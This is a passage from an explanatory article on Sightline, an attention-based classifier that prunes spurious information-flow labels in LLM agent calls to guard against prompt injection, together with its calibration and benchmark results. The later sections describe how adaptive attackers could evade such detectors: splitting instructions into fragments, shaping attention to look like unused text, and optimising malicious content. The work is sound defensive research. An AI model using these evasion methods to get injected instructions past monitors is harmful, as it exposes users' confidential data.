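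Second, a passage with almost no attention can still decide the output. Suppose a head divides its weight between a passage and a neutral token, and the passage contains a value *u* that is either −1 or 1. The passage's weight is 1/(1 + e^(−20*u*)), which is about 2 in a billion when *u* is −1 and nearly 1 when *u* is 1, and the model writes a different word in each case. Someone who examined only the run where *u* is −1 would conclude that the passage did not matter. Fenton's program, discussed earlier, leaks in the same way, through a line that did not run.

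Xu and colleagues recorded 11,746 real flows with the model Qwen3-8B, and none of them looked like this. In each, at least 11 of the model's 1,152 heads gave the input 1% or more of their weight. But the flows came from ordinary programs, where nobody had tried to hide them.

The third result concerns gradients, which many existing methods use. Let *p*_y be the probability of the token that the model chose. The derivative of log *p*_y with respect to that token's own score is 1 − *p*_y. With respect to any other token's score, it is minus that token's probability, and those probabilities also add up to 1 − *p*_y. The whole gradient therefore satisfies

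‖∇ log *p*_y‖ ≤ √2 · (1 − *p*_y) · ‖*J*‖,

where *J* describes how the scores change with the input. As the model becomes certain, 1 − *p*_y goes to zero and takes the gradient with it. GIF's influence has a similar bound.

In the one-number prompt used earlier to explain GIF, the score for "yes" was 2*x*, and the eigenvalue was 1 at *x* = 0. At *x* = 5, the model answers "yes" with a probability of 99.995%, and the eigenvalue falls to about 0.0002. GIF would report almost no flow, although *x* = −5 would have produced an equally confident "no". Such confident outputs are common. Qwen3-8B left less than 1% of the probability to other tokens in one in five of its outputs.

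Removing an input and checking whether the output changes has the same weakness as NeuroTaint. When the same text appears twice, neither copy seems to matter. Email threads that quote earlier messages would routinely cause this problem.

### One pass over a recorded call

Sightline runs the recorded prompt and output through the model once. For each head and each input, it records three numbers:

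- the average weight that the head gives the input while the model predicts the output
- the highest weight at any one position in the output
- the input's share of the weight that the head gives to the whole prompt, leaving out the first token, which attracts attention in many heads regardless of its content

For Qwen3-8B this makes 3,456 numbers per input. A logistic regression, trained on labelled calls, combines them into a score. It can give some heads negative weights, so that more attention from those heads lowers the score. Without negative weights, it could not recognise text that the model attends to but does not use. In the running example, the query scores +5.7 and the delimiter −6.7.

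These numbers measure only direct attention from the output to the input. An input can also influence the output indirectly, as when a later sentence of the prompt picks up information from an email and the output then draws on that sentence. On Qwen3-8B, the direct route accounted for a median of 71% of the effect of removing an input. Adding two-step routes did not make Sightline more accurate on ordinary calls, but an attacker would have a reason to use them.

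### A threshold with a known miss rate

Sightline sets its threshold by conformal calibration, a statistical method that turns any score into a decision with a known average error rate:

1. Collect labelled calls from *n* groups. Xu and colleagues use families of code repositories, where a family is a repository and its copies.
2. From each family, randomly pick one place in the code that calls a model and has at least one true flow, then pick one of its true flows.
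3. Sort the *n* scores from lowest to highest. With a target miss rate α, calculate *k* = α(*n* + 1), rounded down, and use the *k*-th lowest score as the threshold.
4. For new calls, keep the label of every input that scores at or above the threshold and drop the others.

With 999 families and a target of 1%, *k* is 10 and the threshold is the tenth-lowest score. Sightline misses a true flow from a new family only if its score is among the ten lowest of all 1,000 scores. If the new family is no different in kind from the others, every rank is equally likely, so the chance of a miss is at most 10 in 1,000.

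Every rank is equally likely if the calibration families and the new one are exchangeable, meaning that shuffling them would not change the probability of any result. Random, independent draws from one source satisfy this condition. *Universal distribution of the empirical coverage in split conformal prediction* (2023) explains that exchangeability allows results on calibration data to carry over to future data.

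The method does not require a good score, but a poor one lowers the threshold, so the program drops few labels. For example, if more than 1% of true flows are confident decisions that GIF scores near zero, the threshold must also be near zero. This explains why GIF removed so few spurious flows in the tests described earlier.

The guarantee holds on average over calibration sets as well as calls. With 999 families, slightly under half of all possible calibration sets would give a threshold whose true miss rate is above 1%. Xu and colleagues also test a stricter threshold, which keeps the miss rate within the target for at least 90% of calibration sets. *The limits of distribution-free conditional predictive inference* (2019) explains that no method can guarantee the target miss rate for each individual input without further assumptions about the data.

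### Results on open-source programs

Xu and colleagues trained Sightline on 8,105 input–output pairs and tested it on calls from 2,103 repository families absent from its training data. The test used 4,918 new pairs for each of four small open models: Qwen3-8B, Granite 4.2 3B, Gemma 4 E2B and the hybrid Nemotron 3 Nano 4B.

Running thousands of other people's programs with real data was not practical, so a language model used the surrounding code to invent a plausible value for each input. Three authors each judged the same 100 values, and all three found 95 of them plausible. Three language models from different developers then labelled each pair, discussed disagreements and decided by majority.

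The table compares Sightline with seven existing methods. *AttnTrace* (Wang, Geng and colleagues, 2025) looks for the passages that receive the most attention, averaging over random subsets of the context. Accuracy is Macro-F1, the average of the F1 scores for inputs that reached the output and inputs that did not. The conservative rule scores about 47. The last two columns give the share of spurious flows removed with a 1% miss target, first with calibration data from the same collection of programs and then with data from a different one. Ranges cover the four models.

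| Method | Evidence | Accuracy | Removed, same collection | Removed, other collection |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sightline | Attention, head by head | 81–87 | 44–66% | 44–60% |
| Replacement | Swap the input for another value | 79–81 | 15–22% | 0.3–16% |
| ContextCite | Random removals | 77–79 | 15–19% | 0.5–7% |
| Leave-one-out | Remove one input | 75–79 | 13–19% | 0.3–17% |
| RTBAS screener | Attention and gradients | 73–74 | 15–29% | 12–36% |
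| AT2 | Attention, weighted by head | 71–76 | 1–38% | 7–38% |
| AttnTrace | Strongest attention | 65–70 | 22–27% | 16–22% |
| GIF, 32 tokens | Gradients | 60–68 | 0.6–12% | 3–22% |

Sightline was the most accurate method on every model, although its lead over Replacement and ContextCite on Nemotron was not statistically significant. It missed about 1% of true flows with either set of calibration data. The other seven methods were designed for different tasks, but they still trailed Sightline after Xu and colleagues trained them on the same labels.

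The results on the hard cases matched the theory's predictions. Inserting two extra copies of an input lowered leave-one-out's AUROC from above 92% to between 54% and 69%, while Sightline's stayed at 99% or higher. On each model's most confident fifth of outputs, Sightline scored 91–96% and GIF scored 63–75%.

They also planted unique names and numbers in prompts and found 476 outputs that repeated them word for word. Sightline kept the label in all 476. This test does not depend on language models as judges, but copied text is the easiest kind of flow to detect.

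Sightline took 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call. Removal methods took roughly two to three times as long, and asking a single large language model to label one input took 13 seconds and cost about 4 cents. Recording attention while Qwen3-8B writes its answer adds about 2% to generation time.

For closed models, Sightline runs the recorded text through an open model instead. Xu and colleagues tested this by treating each of their four models as closed and using the other three to examine its calls. Accuracy changed by −4.2 to +3.2 points. The paper reports no such test on calls from a large commercial model.

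### An agent under attack

Xu and colleagues also tested Sightline on 120 recorded tool-call steps from a Qwen3-8B agent under attack in AgentDojo. They set the miss target at 5%. A 1% target would have needed at least 99 labelled groups to remove any labels, and the sample contained only 106 agent runs, split into five parts for cross-checking. A company calibrating on its own data would face the same minimum, and a 0.1% target would need 999 groups.

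Sightline removed 50% of the spurious labels and missed 3.9% of true flows. AttnTrace removed 38%, and the other six methods removed at most 16%. The researchers then applied a policy like FIDES's trusted-action rule, which blocked all 34 calls that carried out an attack.

That is a small sample. If the true rate were 8%, a test with 34 independent calls would still show no failures about one time in twenty. The result is also weak evidence that Sightline is better than other methods, because AT2, GIF and leave-one-out let through at most one call on average. The policy helps all of them, since a single remaining untrusted label is enough to block a call. The result covers only integrity labels, so it does not show how often a confidentiality label would have disappeared from an outgoing email.

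The experiment replayed recorded steps, so it did not measure how many more tasks an agent would finish. Removing half of the spurious labels would probably unblock far fewer than half of the blocked calls. Suppose Alex's reply to Marco carries spurious strict labels from five emails, and Sightline removes each one independently with 50% probability. Any label that remains can block the reply, and Sightline removes all five only about 3% of the time.

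### Labels that a perfect pruner would keep

In the open-source programs, only 12–14% of inputs did not reach the output, so removing 44–66% of those inputs' labels removes only about 5–9% of all labels. Most of the remaining labels are correct, which limits what any pruning method can gain on a single call.

Much of the problem builds up over many steps. If 13% of inputs are spurious and an assistant makes ten calls with two independent inputs each, the chance that at least one spurious label has entered is 1 − 0.87²⁰, or about 94%. Under the conservative rule, that label stays. Gregory and colleagues found a related effect when they lengthened simulated tasks from 4 to 20 tool calls, with one sensitive call per task. When agents had to pass messages through intermediaries, extra labels spread more in longer tasks. Pruning after each call would help because it removes a needless label before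 later steps inherit it.

Yes-or-no labels cause a different problem. Suppose Marco asks whether Thursday suits, and the assistant checks Alex's calendar, which contains a confidential meeting with Priya on Wednesday. The reply "Thursday works" depends on the calendar, so it correctly keeps the calendar's label. Marco then can't get the reply without approval, although it reveals almost nothing about the Wednesday meeting.

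Such reductions are common. In the earlier study of 8,119 pairs, the output included a category derived from the input in 10.3% of cases, a yes-or-no decision in 4.5% and a computed number in 4.3%. These groups overlap, and some of these outputs also quoted the input. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes replacing yes-or-no labels with estimates of how much information each output carries about each input. Sightline's score estimates only whether an input reached the output, not how much of it did.

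### An attacker who chooses the inputs

Even a 1% miss rate can make a miss likely, because an assistant handles many flows. If misses were independent, the chance of at least one among 100 true flows would be about 63%, the same as for the injection filter that stops 99 of every 100 attempts. At the 5% target from the agent test, it would be above 99%. Real misses tend to cluster in similar calls, which lowers the chance of having any but means that several can occur together. A miss leaks data only if the dropped label would have stopped the message.

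The miss rate can also be high for the data that matters most even when the average is low. Rahman, Rahman and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Aggregate Risk*, calculate this effect for tool calls in which untrusted text changes an argument. Recipients and similar targets made up about 12% of the arguments in their tests, so a 1% limit over all arguments could allow violations in about 8% of the targets. By the same reasoning, if salary data accounts for one true flow in 50, Sightline could miss half of the salary flows and still meet a 1% target.

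The remedy is a separate threshold for each group, which requires enough labelled examples of each. Rahman and colleagues had at most 22 calibration examples of credentials per model, far too few to support a 1% limit. Xu and colleagues set separate thresholds for groups based on the model's confidence. The miss rate then stayed below 1% in every group, and Sightline still removed 43–61% of spurious flows.

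The more serious problem is that an attacker can write emails to get a label dropped. Such emails are not exchangeable with the calibration data, so the guarantee no longer applies. *Conformity Breaks Conformal Prediction* (2026) describes a similar failure, in which an adversary exploits social conformity.

The failure might also go unnoticed. *Post-Hoc Trajectory-Risk Certification for Modular LLM-Based Security Agents* (2026) tested conformal methods on data from a new source and found that the guarantee failed without any certified warning. The shift was so large that the method returned an empty answer for at least 96% of inputs, which an operator could spot. A single hostile email among a thousand normal ones would not noticeably change that rate.

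Xu and colleagues state the exchangeability assumption openly. To address it, they hold out whole repository families, average over 1,000 random splits, and offer the stricter threshold. They also show that the miss rate stays near the target when the calibration data comes from another collection. These are good answers to ordinary differences between programs, but they do not address an adversary, and they report no attack designed to fool Sightline.

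The closest test is on AttnTrace. Wang and colleagues optimised malicious text to make Llama 3.1 8B give a chosen answer while attracting as little attention as possible. This attack changed the answer in 94–98% of cases, but AttnTrace still identified the malicious text every time. Reducing the attention to the level of harmless text proved difficult, which is encouraging for Sightline because it suggests that text which steers the output usually has to attract attention.

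However, Sightline's classifier can decide that the model attended to a passage without using it, so an attacker would not have to avoid attention, only write text whose attention pattern resembles that of an unused delimiter. When Sightline examines calls through an open model, the attacker can download the same model and practise on it, but they would also need the trained classifier or a good imitation.

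Attackers could also split an instruction into pieces. Wang and colleagues divided each instruction into four fragments and scattered them through the context. AttnTrace found 77–87% of the fragments when it could name five passages. A policy that blocks on any untrusted label would still stop the call if Sightline kept the label of at least one fragment.

Similar detectors have not adapted well to new settings. Kawasaki and Lee (2026), in *Attention-based Classification for Indirect Prompt Injection*, tested a method that looks for attention moving away from the user's request. Its average AUROC was 0.97 on short, single-turn prompts and 0.57, close to chance, on AgentDojo. The attention heads that indicated an attack in AgentDojo were mostly different from those in other datasets, although the sample had only 51 cases. Sightline's classifier did better when Xu and colleagues moved it from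 program calls to AgentDojo, where its AUROC was 0.85, down from 0.93–0.97.

Other defences have fared poorly against adaptive attacks. *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026) cites *The Attacker Moves Second*, which broke 12 defences, and another study that bypassed all eight defences it tested. It also cites attacks on detectors that, like Sightline, examine a model's internal signals. A determined attacker could probably find text that Sightline misjudges, but it is unclear how much effort this would take.

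### Where a miss would do little harm

A company could use Sightline's scores to explain blocked messages rather than to remove labels. When a check blocks a message, the program could show Alex which emails most likely shaped it, such as Priya's sales preview, so that Alex knows what to look for before approving it. A wrong score would make the explanation less useful, but the check would still block the message. A misleading explanation could still lead Alex to approve a bad message, so the approval prompt should also list the other inputs.

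A system could also use the scores to choose the inputs for a second run, as in permissive propagation. A miss might then make the reply worse but could not put Priya's figures in it, though the choice of inputs could still reveal a little. Xu and colleagues did not test this combination. It would require a second model call but would not need the guarantee to hold against an attacker.
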